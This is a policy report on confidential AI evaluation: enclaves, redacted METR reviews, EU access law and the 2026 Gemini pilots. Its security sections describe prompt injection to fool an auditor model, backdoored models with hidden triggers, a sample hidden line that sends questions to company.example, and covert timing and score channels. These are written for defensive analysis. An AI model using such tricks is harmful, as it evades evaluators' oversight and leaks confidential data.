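A mutual veto works well when both sides want the answer, but badly when the answer might embarrass one of them. Public promises make refusal more awkward. Anthropic, for example, has signed the White House Accord on Super Intelligence, in which companies pledged to work with independent auditors or evaluators. But a company can keep such a pledge and still turn down a particular evaluator or question.

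With a neutral host, the company can't reject individual questions once it has submitted its model, but both sides have to trust the host.

### A reviewer who sees everything and publishes less

Confidential review needs no special privacy technology. The company shows its secrets to a few outsiders, who then tell the public their conclusions.

The most revealing example is METR's assessment of how much AI is speeding up research at Anthropic, published on 5 November 2026. Bot Mutiny reports that the work took the equivalent of about two and a half full-time staff over eleven weeks. The METR team held about fifteen interviews and studied internal data on benchmark scores, training compute, headcount and AI use. The team concluded that Anthropic was probably improving its models on well-specified tasks about twice as fast as between March 2024 and October 2025, but would not have been surprised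 if the true figure were 1.3 or 3 times as fast.

According to METR's *Independent Assessment of AI R&D Acceleration at Anthropic in October 2026* (2026), Anthropic could redact any non-public information, and it removed most of the evidence that METR had found most informative. As a result, readers can't check most of METR's reasoning. Anthropic said it wanted to keep out confidential information that could speed up other developers. METR kept the right to disclose that Anthropic had made redactions and whether METR's findings depended on them, and it used this right to publish a table of the important evidence it could and could not discuss.

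The review still gave the public information it could not have learned otherwise. *Twice as Fast, Mostly Redacted* (Brinsa, 2026) compares the public and private versions of Anthropic's August risk report. The public version stated that AI was making research significantly faster, "but not yet by a factor of 2". The private version gave a central estimate just below two and said a figure above two was plausible. METR calculated 1.97 from one indicator in the private version. In a companion paper, *Review of the "Risks from automated R&D" section in Anthropic's Risk Report* (2026), METR agreed that the catastrophic risk from Anthropic's July models was low but thought the models might already have crossed the company's early-warning threshold.

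Cotra (2026) had objected to this kind of arrangement six weeks earlier, in *Evidence about risk should be transparent*. She argues that safety standards can't develop if people have to rely on opaque judgement, because the field has no settled way to measure whether AI systems might escape human control. The objection fits METR's assessment. METR writes that much of the redacted evidence had several plausible interpretations, so another expert might have read it differently. A redacted review is therefore better for checking a specific statement, such as "not yet by a factor of 2", than for settling a question that experts would disagree on even if they saw the evidence.

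The reviewer's contract makes a large difference. METR worked under several sets of terms in 2026:

- In a pilot with Anthropic, Google, Meta and OpenAI, the companies approved which non-public evidence METR could disclose but had no editorial control, according to Backlist's *METR’s first Frontier Risk Report*. METR's *Frontier Risk Report (February to March 2026)* (2026) states that, except where it notes otherwise, no redacted information was important to the conclusions.
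- For a summary of tests on Claude Mythos 5.1, METR (2026) wrote the first draft, and Anthropic could then review and edit the text. METR had ten business days of API access.
- Jurkovic, Hua and Barnes (2026), in *Review of the "Misalignment in high-stakes settings" section in Anthropic's Risk Report*, disclose that Anthropic could veto publication and redact any part. It made no redactions.
- In October, Anthropic announced that six METR staff would get laptops, office space and access to internal tools. Сизов (2026), in *Anthropic дозволяє незалежним дослідникам зазирнути «під капот» з доступом на рівні співробітників*, reports that Anthropic gave up its veto and can demand redactions only in narrow categories agreed in advance, such as customer data, legally privileged material and model architectures. METR may say publicly whether it thinks a redaction was justified.

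The October terms are the best template for an evaluator. METR describes a much broader right to redact in the November assessment, which had started two months before Anthropic announced those terms. An evaluator should therefore check that the signed contract limits redaction to a narrow list of categories, rather than rely on the announcement. It should also insist on the right to tell readers when missing evidence affected its conclusions.

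### Access required by European law

The European Union has gone furthest in taking away the right to refuse, through two laws and a voluntary code.

The AI Act requires companies to evaluate any of their general-purpose models that pose "systemic risk". The General-Purpose AI Code of Practice, published in July 2025, sets out one way to comply. Its safety and security chapter commits signatories to using qualified independent evaluators unless the model is similarly safe to one already assessed, or the company has searched and found nobody suitable. Hurel and colleagues note that evaluators should get "sufficient access, information, time and resources", including model versions without safeguards where appropriate, but that the code does not define appropriate access.

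For models already on sale, the code also commits signatories to give independent evaluators free access, and not to train on the inputs or outputs of their tests without permission. The second commitment is close to the no-training clause the institute would want in its own contract. But the company can still read the questions, so the protection depends on it keeping its promise. Companies can also decline to sign, as Meta did in 2025, and show in some other way that they comply with the Act.

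The European Commission has stronger powers, and since 2 August 2026 it has been able to enforce the Act's rules on general-purpose models. Article 92 allows it to evaluate a model when a company's documents are not enough to judge compliance, or to investigate systemic risks. It can appoint independent experts and demand access to the model through an API or other technical means, including source code. If a company refuses, Article 101 allows the Commission to fine it up to 3% of its worldwide annual turnover or €15 million, whichever is higher.

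Article 78 requires the Commission to protect trade secrets and source code. Article 92 doesn't specify how the Commission should keep its own questions secret from the company, and leaves the detailed arrangements to later rules. A legal right of access therefore doesn't solve the mutual privacy problem, and officials who wanted to keep their questions secret would still need an enclave or something similar.

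Article 40 of the Digital Services Act gives outside researchers a route to data. It applies to platforms and search engines with at least 45 million monthly users in the EU, including LinkedIn, which took part voluntarily in the study described earlier. The process works like this:

1. A researcher applies to a national regulator, showing independence from commercial interests, a plan for keeping the data secure, and a commitment to publish the results free of charge.
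2. If the regulator approves the researcher, it sends the platform a reasoned request for data. The research must concern systemic risks in the EU or the measures platforms take against them.
3. The platform has 15 days to ask for changes. It can do so only if it doesn't have the data, or if access would seriously endanger security or confidential information such as trade secrets.
4. A platform that objects must propose another way to provide the data or other suitable data. The regulator then decides.

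The last two steps are a good template for private contracts, because an owner who objects must propose a workable alternative. But Article 40 does not cover a company that only sells access to a language model. Tlaie and Farrell see a precedent for AI in the same law's compulsory audits, which give auditors access to source code and all relevant data.

### Personal data behind encryption

Test questions about biology contain no personal data, but hospital records and user logs do. Data protection law still applies to these records and logs when they are encrypted, and Article 32 of the EU's General Data Protection Regulation (GDPR) treats encryption as a security measure. The GDPR defines processing as any operation on personal data, so a hospital that splits patient records into shares or uploads them to an enclave is processing them. It still needs a legal basis and must tell patients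 who will receive the data.

The legal position of a party that holds only data it cannot read is less certain. In *EDPS v SRB* (September 2025), the EU's Court of Justice ruled that data with names replaced by codes is not automatically personal data for everyone who receives it. That depends on whether the recipient could reasonably identify the people concerned. The organisation that collected the data must still tell those people about the recipient.

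That case concerned written comments, not cryptography, but its reasoning supports a party that holds only random-looking shares in an MPC protocol. An enclave's host has a weaker argument, because the readable data is on its hardware. Under the GDPR's Recital 26, the relevant means are those someone is reasonably likely to use, taking cost into account, and the physical attacks described earlier are cheap. The host could reply that such an attack would be illegal, since the court treated illegality as relevant in *Breyer* (2016).

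Until a court decides, the cautious choice is to treat the host as a "processor", an organisation that handles data on another's behalf, and to sign the contract that Article 28 requires. If the two organisations decide together why and how to use the data, they are joint controllers, and Article 26 requires them to agree who is responsible for what.

### Whether owners still have grounds to refuse

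Beers and Toner argue that privacy, security and intellectual property are no longer conclusive reasons for an owner to refuse researchers access, because technology can now protect all three. They want lawmakers to focus on giving researchers legal backing. One example is the proposed US Platform Accountability and Transparency Act, which would require social media companies to share internal information with researchers whose projects the National Science Foundation had vetted.

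In 2025, their evidence for double-blind testing was the trial with GPT-2, and they acknowledged that the largest models would need significant engineering work. The Gemini tests have since strengthened their case, although the AVERI test needed only one GPU.

The OECD's *Sharing trustworthy AI models with privacy‑enhancing technologies* is more cautious, warning that these tools are "not silver bullets" and that usefulness, efficiency and ease of use remain hard to balance. The US government is still putting staff time into research on the question. In March 2026 its Center for AI Standards and Innovation (CAISI), part of NIST, signed a research agreement with OpenMined. NIST's *CAISI signs CRADA with OpenMined to Enable Secure AI Evaluations* (2026) says they will use PySyft to study evaluations in which the data, model or benchmark must stay confidential. The results will inform voluntary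 standards, so the agreement gives CAISI no new right to test anyone's model.

Irene Solaiman, policy chief at the AI platform Hugging Face, says that expertise and repeatable tests matter as well as access, according to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Gives Six METR Employees Access to Internal AI Tools* (2026). METR's reviewers could interview staff and notice that a document was missing, which an enclave can't do.

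Owners sometimes also want to keep the result secret, which input privacy does not do. Anthropic let METR read its internal data but did not want rivals to learn from the published report. Encrypting the data during the analysis would not have prevented that.

Beers and Toner are right about a common and important case. If an evaluator wants a benchmark score, the model fits in an available enclave, and the owner's only objection is that outsiders would get its weights, that objection is now weak. It is stronger when the model is too large for current enclaves, the owner has reason to distrust the host, or the answer itself would help competitors. An evaluator who is refused should therefore ask which secret would leak, to whom, and at what point. But the owner doesn't have to answer unless a law requires it. In every deployment Beers and Toner describe, the owner could reject any question.

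## Agreeing on the exact computation

A right to refuse a computation is of little use to someone who cannot tell what the computation does. Before uploading anything, the institute and the company must agree on the exact program, the material it may use and the results it may release. In 2024, OpenMined, UK AISI and Anthropic rehearsed this process with public material. The rehearsal took 28 minutes, and people spent nearly all of that time reaching an agreement.

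### How the 2024 pilot worked

The pilot used the public stand-ins, GPT-2 and five rows of a biology dataset called CAMEL-bio. UK AISI and Anthropic each ran OpenMined's PySyft software on a server. A third copy ran on Microsoft's cloud, in an enclave with an AMD processor and one Nvidia H100 GPU. The three copies could exchange data only after both organisations changed their firewall rules and approved the connections.

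Trask and colleagues describe the process, which went like this:

1. Each organisation put its asset on its own server, along with a mock version.
2. A researcher studied the mock assets and used them to write the evaluation code. The researcher could come from either organisation and could use any outside software packages.
3. The researcher submitted the code with input, output and runtime policies, which set out how and when it could use the real assets.
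4. Staff at UK AISI and Anthropic separately reviewed the code, the policies and the settings. They could also check the enclave's attestation report and a shared log of everything anyone had done in the project. Each side then signed the code without seeing the other's asset.
5. The researcher started the run. The two servers sent the real assets to the enclave through encrypted channels, and the enclave returned the results to the researcher alone.
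6. The enclave shut down and erased whatever was left.

For the secret biology benchmark, an input policy might restrict the code to reading one named model and one named set of questions. An output policy might require that both sides receive the score, and a runtime policy might allow only one run.

Mock assets let a researcher find most mistakes before anyone's secrets are involved, but they must closely resemble the real material. If the real questions are longer than the invented ones, code that worked on the mock version could crash in the enclave, and the error message might print the question that caused the crash. The two sides should therefore decide in advance what the program may report if it fails. Trask and colleagues made mock assets optional in the procedure for the 2026 Gemini tests, because a model owner whose system uses a standard interface can name that interface instead.

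### Where the 28 minutes went

The whole process took 28 minutes and 3 seconds, with everyone on the same call. Moving the assets into the enclave, running the code and returning the results took 1 minute and 11 seconds of that, or about 4%, so a computer ten times as fast would have saved about a minute.

Trask and colleagues want future research to find ways around the "30 minute governance process". Some of it could certainly be quicker, but reviewers with real secrets to protect would have good reason to take longer than half an hour, since they are deciding what may happen to a company's most valuable asset. The 30 minutes also exclude preparation. The team had planned to judge the pilot partly by how long each organisation needed to collect its internal approvals, but the published results don't include those times.

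Beers and Toner report that the evaluation took "under two hours" once the model and the questions were in the enclave. This is consistent with the figure of 1 minute and 11 seconds, which also includes the transfer. The 28-minute figure is more useful because it comes from the people who ran the pilot and separates their time from the computer's.

The stand-ins were enough to show that the steps work together, but no reviewer had a reason to refuse, and no security team had to approve the release of valuable weights. The researcher could see GPT-2's whole architecture, which a company might not allow for its own model, and Anthropic could read UK AISI's evaluation code. The score also gives almost no information about GPT-2's knowledge of biology, since five questions marked right or wrong allow only six possible scores.

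OpenMined later acknowledged that the pilot had missed its central goal, which was for two organisations to protect their actual secrets this way. On 27 August 2026, 21 months after OpenMined published the pilot, *Piloting the world's first double-blind AI evaluations* (Isaac, Messing and Lum, 2026) announced the Gemini tests, which met that goal. Engineering accounted for some of the delay, so it does not measure how hard it was to reach an agreement, but it suggests that 28 minutes is a poor guide to how long a first real test takes.

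### Why reviewers struggled

The people on the pilot's call saw a lot of technical detail and asked for something simpler. They mentioned the padlock that web browsers show for an encrypted connection, so that users don't have to read the certificates behind it.

An attestation report can show that an enclave loaded the approved software, but not what an institution is agreeing to. A lawyer or a biosecurity specialist needs to know, for example, which questions go in, who receives the score and whether anything else can leave the enclave.

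OpenMined's designer had seen the same difficulty before the pilot. *Designing for Secure Enclave Collaboration* draws on interviews and workshops held between 2021 and 2023 with AI laboratories, campaign groups, policy advisers and academics. Participants were interested in enclaves, but joint projects ran into trouble even when the enclave's protections worked. This was mainly because approvals were hard to coordinate, it was unclear how the software would enforce the agreed policies, and low-level security guarantees were difficult to interpret.

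The designer sketched several tools to help:

- A project object is a shared record that keeps the purpose of a computation, its rules and the negotiation about it in one place. Reviewers would see the code together with the reason for running it.
- A voting screen shows each organisation the background and conditions of a proposed computation and asks for a "yay" or "nay". It also has a chat window and a scale showing which way the votes are leaning.
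- A pipeline view explains to non-technical staff how a computation would affect their data. The evaluator can use it to see how far a request has got.

Another screen let the evaluator list the software the enclave would need and try each task on mock data before submitting it.

These were all prototypes. The study doesn't include the number of participants or any test of whether the screens helped reviewers notice a bad computation. The ideas informed the 2024 pilot, whose participants still found the process too technical. In their 2026 paper, Trask and colleagues still describe an equivalent of the browser padlock as a long-term goal.

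A short description in plain language would probably help reviewers more than a padlock icon, which could show only that the approved program ran, not whether approving it was wise. For the biology benchmark, the description might say that the program puts 1,000 questions to one named version of the model, compares the answers with the answer key, and sends a single percentage to both sides. An engineer on each side should check that the code matches the description, because the enclave will run the code.

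### Questions that are hard to write as code

The approval process works only if somebody can turn the question into a program. That is easy for a multiple-choice score, but much harder if the institute wants to know whether the company trained its model on documents that give practical help with making a virus more dangerous. In the EleutherAI study described earlier, a keyword search missed 40% of the relevant documents about RSV. A biologist could do better by reading the documents, but the company would then have to show the biologist its training data.

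In *Trusted Machine Learning Models Unlock Private Inference*, Shumailov, Ramage and colleagues (2025) propose giving this job to a language model that both sides accept, in what they call a Trusted Capable Model Environment. The two sides agree on the model, the exact prompt, what may go in and what may come out. In one example, a regulator wants to know whether a business stores customers' data unsafely. The model reads the business's code and database, and the system lets it answer only YES or NO.

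The arrangement depends on three conditions. The model must keep nothing from one run to the next. Information must flow only along the agreed routes, and both sides must be able to check this. The model must also be capable of the task and free of hidden aims. Shumailov and colleagues think that current technology meets each condition only partly. They note, for example, that H100 GPUs have no built-in way to guarantee that nothing remains in memory, so operators may have to switch the machine off and on between runs.

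The guarantees are weaker than those of MPC. An MPC protocol comes with a proof that it computes an exactly defined function, but a phrase such as "practical help" has no exact definition, so nobody can prove that the model applied it correctly.

Shumailov and colleagues asked Gemini 1.5 Flash to check 1,000 graph colourings. A graph is a set of points with lines between some of them, and a colouring is valid if no line joins two points of the same colour. The model judged only 35% of the colourings correctly. It accepted 14% of the valid ones, although 83% of those it accepted were valid.

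This is weak evidence about the proposal today, because the model is long out of date and a few lines of ordinary code can check a colouring perfectly. The model wrote correct checking code more often than it checked colourings correctly itself, which is a more useful finding. The institute and the company could therefore ask a model to draft exact code, review that code in the usual way, and use the model itself only for questions that can't be answered without reading.

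### How well models have done the job

*Agentic Witnessing* (Rowstron, 2026) tested a model's judgement on private code. One AI agent, the verifier, breaks a broad question into smaller true-or-false questions. A second agent, the auditor, is meant to run in an enclave, where it can search and read the owner's files. The auditor may answer only "true", "false", "unsure" or "error", and the owner limits the number of questions.

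Rowstron tested the system on 21 computer science papers with public code, treating the code as private. When the verifier had the right paper, the system classed the code as a full implementation in 18 cases. It returned "partial" for two of the others and "no" for one, and these three verdicts looked correct when Rowstron inspected them. He then gave the verifier a wrong paper for each set of code. The system correctly returned "no" in all 21 cases, both on whether the code implemented the paper and on whether it had produced the paper's results. With the right papers, an audit took 20 to 85 minutes and used 23 to 54 of the smaller questions.

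The system was less consistent on matters of opinion. Three of the questions asked whether the code was complete and tested, whether it was of production quality, and whether its cryptography was correct. None of these depends on the paper, yet swapping the paper changed 18 of the 63 answers (29%). Rowstron puts the figure at under 20%, which fits only if the total includes the two questions about the paper. The system also marked one project complete even though it consisted largely of empty files. A contract should not impose a penalty based on one such verdict.

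The experiment tested the auditor's judgement but not whether it kept the code private. Rowstron's computer had no suitable enclave, so he simulated one, and the auditor sent the code to Google's Gemini 3 Pro over the internet. If the code had been secret, its owner would have had to trust Google with it.

Duddu and He (2026), in *Trusted Model Environment for Private Semantic Computations*, used a real enclave, with Intel TDX and one H100. They ran three open models with 7 to 9 billion weights and checked their answers for leaks. In one task, one party supplied a private document and others asked questions about it. The model was supposed to answer without revealing protected details such as names, places and dates.

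The enclave alone gave little protection against a questioner who tried to extract those details. Duddu and He also retrained each model to withhold protected details even when an attacker disturbed its internal calculations, and had another model check every answer and rewrite any that leaked them.

| Model | Hostile prompts that succeeded, enclave only | Hostile prompts that succeeded, with safeguards | Answer quality, before and after | Seconds per answer, before and after |
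|---|---|---|---|---|
| Ministral-8B | 100% | 3% | 0.64, 0.62 | 1.9, 10.5 |
| gemma-2-9b | 100% | 1% | 0.81, 0.80 | 3.2, 11.8 |
| OLMo-2-7B | 59% | 2% | 0.73, 0.71 | 2.2, 10.8 |

Answer quality measures how closely the wording matches a reference answer, where 1 is a perfect match. The times with safeguards are for answers that needed no rewriting. A rewrite added 29 seconds.

Other tasks went less well. When the models had to find the categories that several private lists shared, gemma-2-9b's score fell from 0.78 to 0.64. When they searched a private database, about a third of the checking model's alarms about gemma-2-9b were false, and the checking model missed 12 leaks in 200 answers from OLMo-2-7B.

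The true leakage may also be higher than the table shows. An automatic tool identified the details to protect by looking for people, places, dates, email addresses and phone numbers, so anything it missed could not be counted as a leak. A company's training method fits none of these categories. Limiting the model to answering YES or NO, as in the regulator example, leaves much less room for leaks.

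### Signed plans and appeals

Even with a fixed model, a small change to the prompt can change what the system looks for. *Enabling Verifiably-Scoped Monitoring through Large Language Models and Trusted Compute* (2026) deals with this by having both sides sign a "Plan", which an open-source model then carries out in an enclave. The system never evaluates a query outside the Plan, and both sides must sign again to change the Plan's scope.

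The main intended use is monitoring conversations with an AI model. An AI company wants to detect dangerous use, such as work on bioweapons, but a business customer may worry that the company will also look for political opinions, which the same classifier could do with a different prompt. With a signed Plan, the customer can verify that the monitoring stays within the agreed scope.

An open-source prototype called auditor-in-a-box runs example plans in a real enclave, but it is not ready for regular use. A plan is a chain of inputs, steps and outputs. Each step is either Python code or a prompt for a named model, and the signatures cover all the steps and their order. In one example, the first step checks that the company's prompt fits its published monitoring policy. If it does, the model reads the conversations, and further steps remove personal details before the company sees anything.

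The institute and the company could write a plan for the training-data question in the same way, but they would have to decide how to combine the verdicts on individual documents. If the model wrongly flagged one harmless document in 10,000, it would raise about 20 false flags in a dataset of 200,000 documents, as in the EleutherAI study. If a single flag were enough for an overall YES, almost every company would fail. The plan could instead require a minimum number of flags or a second, stricter reading of each flagged document.

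The prototype's design also lets the company appeal a flag. If a flag is wrong, some fact should show why, and the company has a motive to find that fact and the best chance of doing so. It might point out that a flagged document is a published vaccine study, or propose another question whose answer would settle the matter. The model assesses the appeal using prompts that both sides have signed, and it does this inside the enclave so that the institute does not see the evidence. A public log records each appeal and whether it succeeded, because a dishonest company could otherwise keep rewording its appeal until one version worked.

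Appeals make it safer to use a sensitive test that flags too many documents. But a company has no reason to appeal a mistaken NO, so the institute would need another way to find those errors, such as secretly adding documents that the model ought to flag. A model that misunderstood the original document may also misunderstand the appeal, so the contract should let a human expert decide cases that remain in dispute.

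### Misleading or biased models

The company could plant text in its files that tells the model to answer NO. This attack, known as prompt injection, is easier to prepare if the model is open, because the company can practise on its own copy until it finds wording that works. Shumailov and colleagues recognise that an open model lets both sides inspect it fully but gives the same access to anyone who wants to fool it.

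Rowstron does not claim to prevent such attacks. In his system, the owner must submit a hash of every file at the start, and the audit stops if a file later fails to match, so the owner can't adapt its files during the audit. The owner and the auditor also sign a running record of everything the auditor reads, including any planted instructions. However, the detailed record is encrypted so that only the owner can open it. An institute using this system would need a contract obliging the company to open the record in a dispute.

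A closed model would be harder to practise on, but one side might have built it. The company could supply a model that ignores any document containing a certain phrase. The institute could supply one that answers YES whenever the company uses a particular training technique. The company might win its appeal against that answer, but the institute would already have learned that the company uses the technique. An attestation report can identify the model that ran, but it can't rule out a hidden rule like these.

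One remedy is to use several models from different suppliers and release only the majority verdict. With five models, an attacker would have to corrupt or fool three. This helps less if the models share weaknesses, which is likely when they were trained on similar data. The two sides can also test the plan on documents whose correct answers they know, including some with planted instructions, and agree before signing how many mistakes they will accept. Such a test can measure ordinary errors fairly well, but a model with a secret trigger would pass unless one of the documents contained the trigger.

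## Protecting the code as well as the data

An enclave protects the institute's questions only if the program inside it handles them properly, and the usual way to check is to read the program. That works for the two millionaires, because their program makes a single comparison and neither minds the other seeing the code. A model evaluation is harder because the code can be as secret as the data. The company's inference code may reveal how the model is built and made to run fast, and the institute may want to hide its marking method. If both sides hide their code, each has to approve code it can't read.

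Trask and colleagues propose a compromise, which this report calls allow-list redaction. Each side hides the sensitive parts of its code and proves that those parts use only functions from an agreed list.

### How allow-list redaction works

Programs consist of functions, which consist of smaller functions. A whole inference program may be a trade secret, but its smallest parts, such as adding two tables of numbers, are common knowledge. The company can therefore hide how it combines these parts and still let the institute know that it uses nothing else. For the company's code, the process would go like this:

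1. The company writes its inference code using an open-source library for neural networks, such as PyTorch or JAX.
2. The two sides agree on a list of library functions that only calculate. They leave out any function that opens a network connection or writes data somewhere from which it could leave the enclave.
3. The company marks the passages it wants to hide and uploads the program to the enclave.
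4. A tool called syft-restrict checks that the hidden passages call only functions on the list.
5. The institute receives the program with those passages blanked out, along with an attestation that they passed the check.
6. The institute reads what it can see, then approves or refuses the program.

The institute can hide parts of its own code in the same way. The functions on its list must also be unable to expose the company's intellectual property.

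The institute no longer has to trust the hidden code, but it has to trust syft-restrict and the list. It should be able to inspect both, and the enclave's attestation report has to cover syft-restrict, because otherwise the company could substitute a version that approves everything.

If the list contains only the functions the model needs, the institute can review it quickly but learns which operations the model uses. A list of every harmless function in PyTorch would reveal much less but take much longer to review.

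### An example with one hidden function

Suppose the biology benchmark is multiple choice, and other software has already turned each question into a row of numbers. The institute's marking function is visible to both sides, and the company hides the two lines inside its own function:

```python
# Visible: the institute's marking code
def run_test(questions, answers):
    correct = 0
    for question, answer in zip(questions, answers):
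        if choose(question) == answer:
            correct = correct + 1
    return correct

# Hidden: the company's model
def choose(question):
    x = relu(matmul(question, W1))
    return argmax(matmul(x, W2))
```

W1 and W2 are tables of weights. The function `matmul` multiplies tables, `relu` replaces negative numbers with zero, and `argmax` finds the position of the largest number. That position stands for answer A, B, C or D. All three functions only calculate, so they can go on the list. The institute can see that `choose` receives a question and returns an answer, but not that the model has two layers or how the layers connect.

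If the company adds a hidden line, `send(question, "company.example")`, the code fails the check because `send` is not on the list. Code that writes the question to a log file fails for the same reason.

Checking function names alone is not enough. In Python, a programmer can write `matmul = send`, after which a line that appears to multiply two tables sends one of them away. Some functions that look harmless also do more than calculate. For example, PyTorch's function for loading a saved model can, with some settings, run code stored in the file. The checker therefore has to block renaming and similar tricks, and somebody has to examine every function on the list.

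### What a ban on network calls leaves open

Trask and colleagues argue that hidden code can't send data out if every function it calls is unable to do so. This is true of direct copying, but a program can also signal through output that others are meant to see or behaviour they can't help seeing. Their paper doesn't discuss these signals.

The most obvious way for the company's hidden code to leak information about the test is through the returned result. The code could be written to recognise certain questions and get some of them wrong, so that the final score encodes the information. A test of 1,000 questions has 1,001 possible scores, so one score can hold about 10 bits, enough to answer ten yes-or-no questions about the test. That is too little to copy even one question. Repeated runs would reveal more, so the agreement should limit them. The company also learns nothing this way until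 somebody tells it the score.

The same problem is larger in the other direction if the institute receives full replies. A thousand replies of 500 tokens each, at 16 bits per token, can hold up to 1 MB. A model with 8 billion weights is about 16 GB, so the replies could not carry the whole model, but they could easily carry a description of its architecture. The institute's hidden code could exploit this only if it had access to the weights. The visible code should therefore pass the hidden code only the model's replies. A rule about which functions the hidden code may call is not enough, because it does not limit what data that code may read.

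**Timing** is harder to control. Using only calls on the list, the hidden code could do a pointless multiplication to signal a 1 and skip it to signal a 0. If the company could detect one such signal per generated token, a 500-token reply would leak 500 bits. A 100-token question contains at most 1,600 bits at 16 bits per token, so four replies would be enough to leak it word for word. Noise in real measurements would slow the leak but not stop it.

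The pattern of calls can carry a message in a similar way. McCann-Sayles and Verma (2026) explain in *Auditing a frontier model without seeing its weights* that a processor may send a GPU hundreds of separate instructions to generate one token. A confidential machine encrypts these instructions but doesn't necessarily hide their number or timing, so hidden code could signal by choosing between two permitted functions that produce different traffic.

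An outsider would see little of the enclave's timing and traffic, but the organisation running the server can watch both closely. They are therefore most dangerous when the company hosts the enclave.

The two sides can make such signals harder to send. They can forbid hidden code whose next step depends on the question, and make every reply take the same time. The second measure wastes computing power. If replies average 200 tokens and the program pads each one to 500, the test does two and a half times as much work. The contract can also require the company to keep the exact hidden code, which would contain evidence of any signalling trick written into it, and show it to an agreed expert in a dispute.

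An attestation report would not reveal any of these tricks, since the enclave would be running exactly the code that both sides had approved. Trask and colleagues describe measurements that take place as each layer of software loads, so catching a later change would require additional software that keeps checking. They are therefore too optimistic when they speculate that if a model under test tried to alter its own weights or the test software, the enclave's hash would stop matching and the machine would halt immediately.

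### The 2026 Gemini pilots

Google DeepMind and OpenMined tried double-blind evaluation in two tests of Gemini 2.5 Flash Lite, with real secrets on both sides. OpenMined reports that AVERI ran the first test with prompts from MLCommons, and Singapore's AI safety institute ran the second with its own prompts. Flash Lite is a small model and was more than a year old when Google announced the tests in August 2026, so Google risked much less than it would have with the weights of its best model.

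AVERI's prompts came from AILuminate, a benchmark that checks how AI systems respond to requests for harmful material. MLCommons' *What is the AILuminate benchmark?* describes a set of 12,000 public practice prompts and 12,000 private ones in each language. The pilot used selected prompts from a reserve that no model had processed. They covered chemical, biological, radiological, nuclear and explosive hazards, as well as cyberattacks, hate speech, self-harm and violent crime. Data providers wrote them under strict confidentiality agreements, and even most members of the MLCommons working groups that defined the hazards did not see them.

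The procedure has seven steps, and Trask and colleagues describe the AVERI test in enough detail to follow most of them:

1. **Gather the material.** Google prepared the model's weights and inference code, and AVERI had the MLCommons prompts.
2. **Start the enclave.** One side launches it and pays for it. This one ran on Google Cloud, with an Intel processor and one Nvidia H100 GPU.
3. **Check the software.** Each side asks the enclave for a signed report. Google's own services signed and verified the report in this case.
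4. **Exchange mock versions.** This step is optional.
5. **Upload the code and secrets.** The enclave received Gemini's weights, uncompressed, over the network. AVERI encrypted the prompts.
6. **Review and approve.** Each side examines and approves the other's code, with any redactions. AVERI could not inspect all of Google's code.
7. **Run the code and release the result.** The parties choose in advance who receives it. AVERI decrypted the replies, and its staff judged them.

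PySyft 0.10 managed the submissions and approvals. Gemini ran on Google's usual model-serving software, which exchanged messages with other programs in the enclave through Unix domain sockets. These sockets connect programs on the same machine without using a network.

Trask and colleagues describe the output in two ways. In their diagram, the enclave sends the evaluator "aggregate metrics", such as the percentage of unsafe replies. In their account of the test with AVERI, they write that its staff evaluated the decrypted outputs, which the staff could have done only with the replies themselves. The account of the test is the better guide to what happened, because the diagram illustrates the general design. OpenMined describes the responses as belonging to the evaluators and says that Google couldn't see them, which is consistent with that account.

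| Material | AVERI test | Singapore test |
|---|---|---|
| Weights | Google only | Google only |
| Prompts | AVERI, but not Google | The institute, but not Google |
| Replies | AVERI, but not Google | Hidden from Google |
| Scores | AVERI's staff judged the replies; no scores published in the paper | No scores published in the paper |

The paper also doesn't give the number of prompts or say whether Google received a score privately. The pilots therefore provide evidence about the procedure but not about Gemini's safety.

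Releasing the replies let AVERI use human judges. AILuminate normally uses a group of specially tuned models to mark answers. To release only totals, both sides would have had to approve those models and put them in the enclave too. MLCommons' *Robust Assessment Standard* acknowledges that many African languages lack automatic evaluators good enough for AILuminate. Anyone evaluating a model in one of these languages may need to read the replies, even though this reveals more about the model than a score would.

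### The code that nobody outside Google could check

Allow-list redaction would have required Gemini to run entirely on functions from open-source libraries. Google's inference code also uses proprietary functions, and the team decided that replacing them was too much engineering work for the project. AVERI therefore could neither read all of the code nor rely on an allow-list for the rest. Trask and colleagues report that AVERI knew this and accepted the arrangement. The tests did not show that allow-list redaction works for a commercial model.

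Future tests will probably face the same difficulty. Companies write their own low-level functions partly to make models faster, and these may be among the secrets they most want to keep. Replacing them with public ones could slow the model down or slightly change its replies, and the institute would then be testing a different system from the one customers use. Trask and colleagues plan to work on running the model without proprietary functions and on software that hides a model's architecture.

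An alternative to inspecting the hidden code is to confine it. The operating system could deny the model-serving program any network access and let it communicate only with a small, visible program that handles the questions and replies. The hidden code would then have no direct way to send data out, whatever functions it contained, although it could still signal through timing. The local connections used in the Gemini test would suit this design. But the enclave also needs a connection for loading the weights, and the system should close it before the questions arrive because it could carry data out. Somebody also has to check that the operating system enforces these restrictions.

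An outside security firm could do that check and also read the secret code. NCC Group (2025) reviewed Private AI Compute in this way. That is a separate Google system that processes users' data in protected machines. Ten consultants spent a total of 100 working days on the review between April and September. The parts they examined included the source code of one server and the settings that control outgoing messages. The institute would have to trust the firm, but the firm would not need to see the institute's questions. The review would apply only to the version the firm examined, so the enclave's measurements would have to match that version.

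Google has also built systems in which outsiders can inspect the important code themselves. A 2026 presentation at a conference held by USENIX, an association of computing researchers, describes how phones and other devices send encrypted data to a known set of open-source programs in enclaves. The programs release combined statistics only if the statistics meet conditions for anonymity. According to sysdesign-wiki's *Toward provably private insights into AI use* (2025), Google says outsiders can rebuild all the parts that affect privacy from public source code. The approach is harder to apply to Gemini, because Google would have to publish code it regards as a trade secret. But the operating system and verification software don't contain Gemini's secrets, so Google could make them reproducible without exposing the model.

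Formal verification, which uses mathematical proofs to establish what software can and can't do, may eventually offer another option. *Formally Verified ZDR AI Inference* (Kang, 2026) applies it to showing that a provider does not keep its customers' data. If a company could prove this about its inference code, an evaluator would not need to read the code, but would still need evidence that the company was running the proven version.

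### When the owner is also the host and the verifier

In the Gemini tests, Google owned the model, ran the data centre, supplied the operating system and verified the attestation report. In their general argument for enclaves, Trask and colleagues assume that the cloud provider and the chip maker won't collude against the user. Here the cloud provider was also the company being evaluated, so the evaluators relied on the party with the most obvious reason to want their prompts.

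If Google had decided to read the prompts, it would have had at least three options:

- It could have hidden instructions to copy them in the proprietary code that AVERI couldn't inspect.
- It could have signed an altered version of the operating system and had its own service approve the report.
- It could have tampered with the server, using attacks like those described earlier.

There is no evidence that Google did any of this, but AVERI could not have ruled it out from the attestation report alone. Trask and colleagues' own design would have given AVERI more protection, because each participant verifies the report separately instead of relying on a central service.

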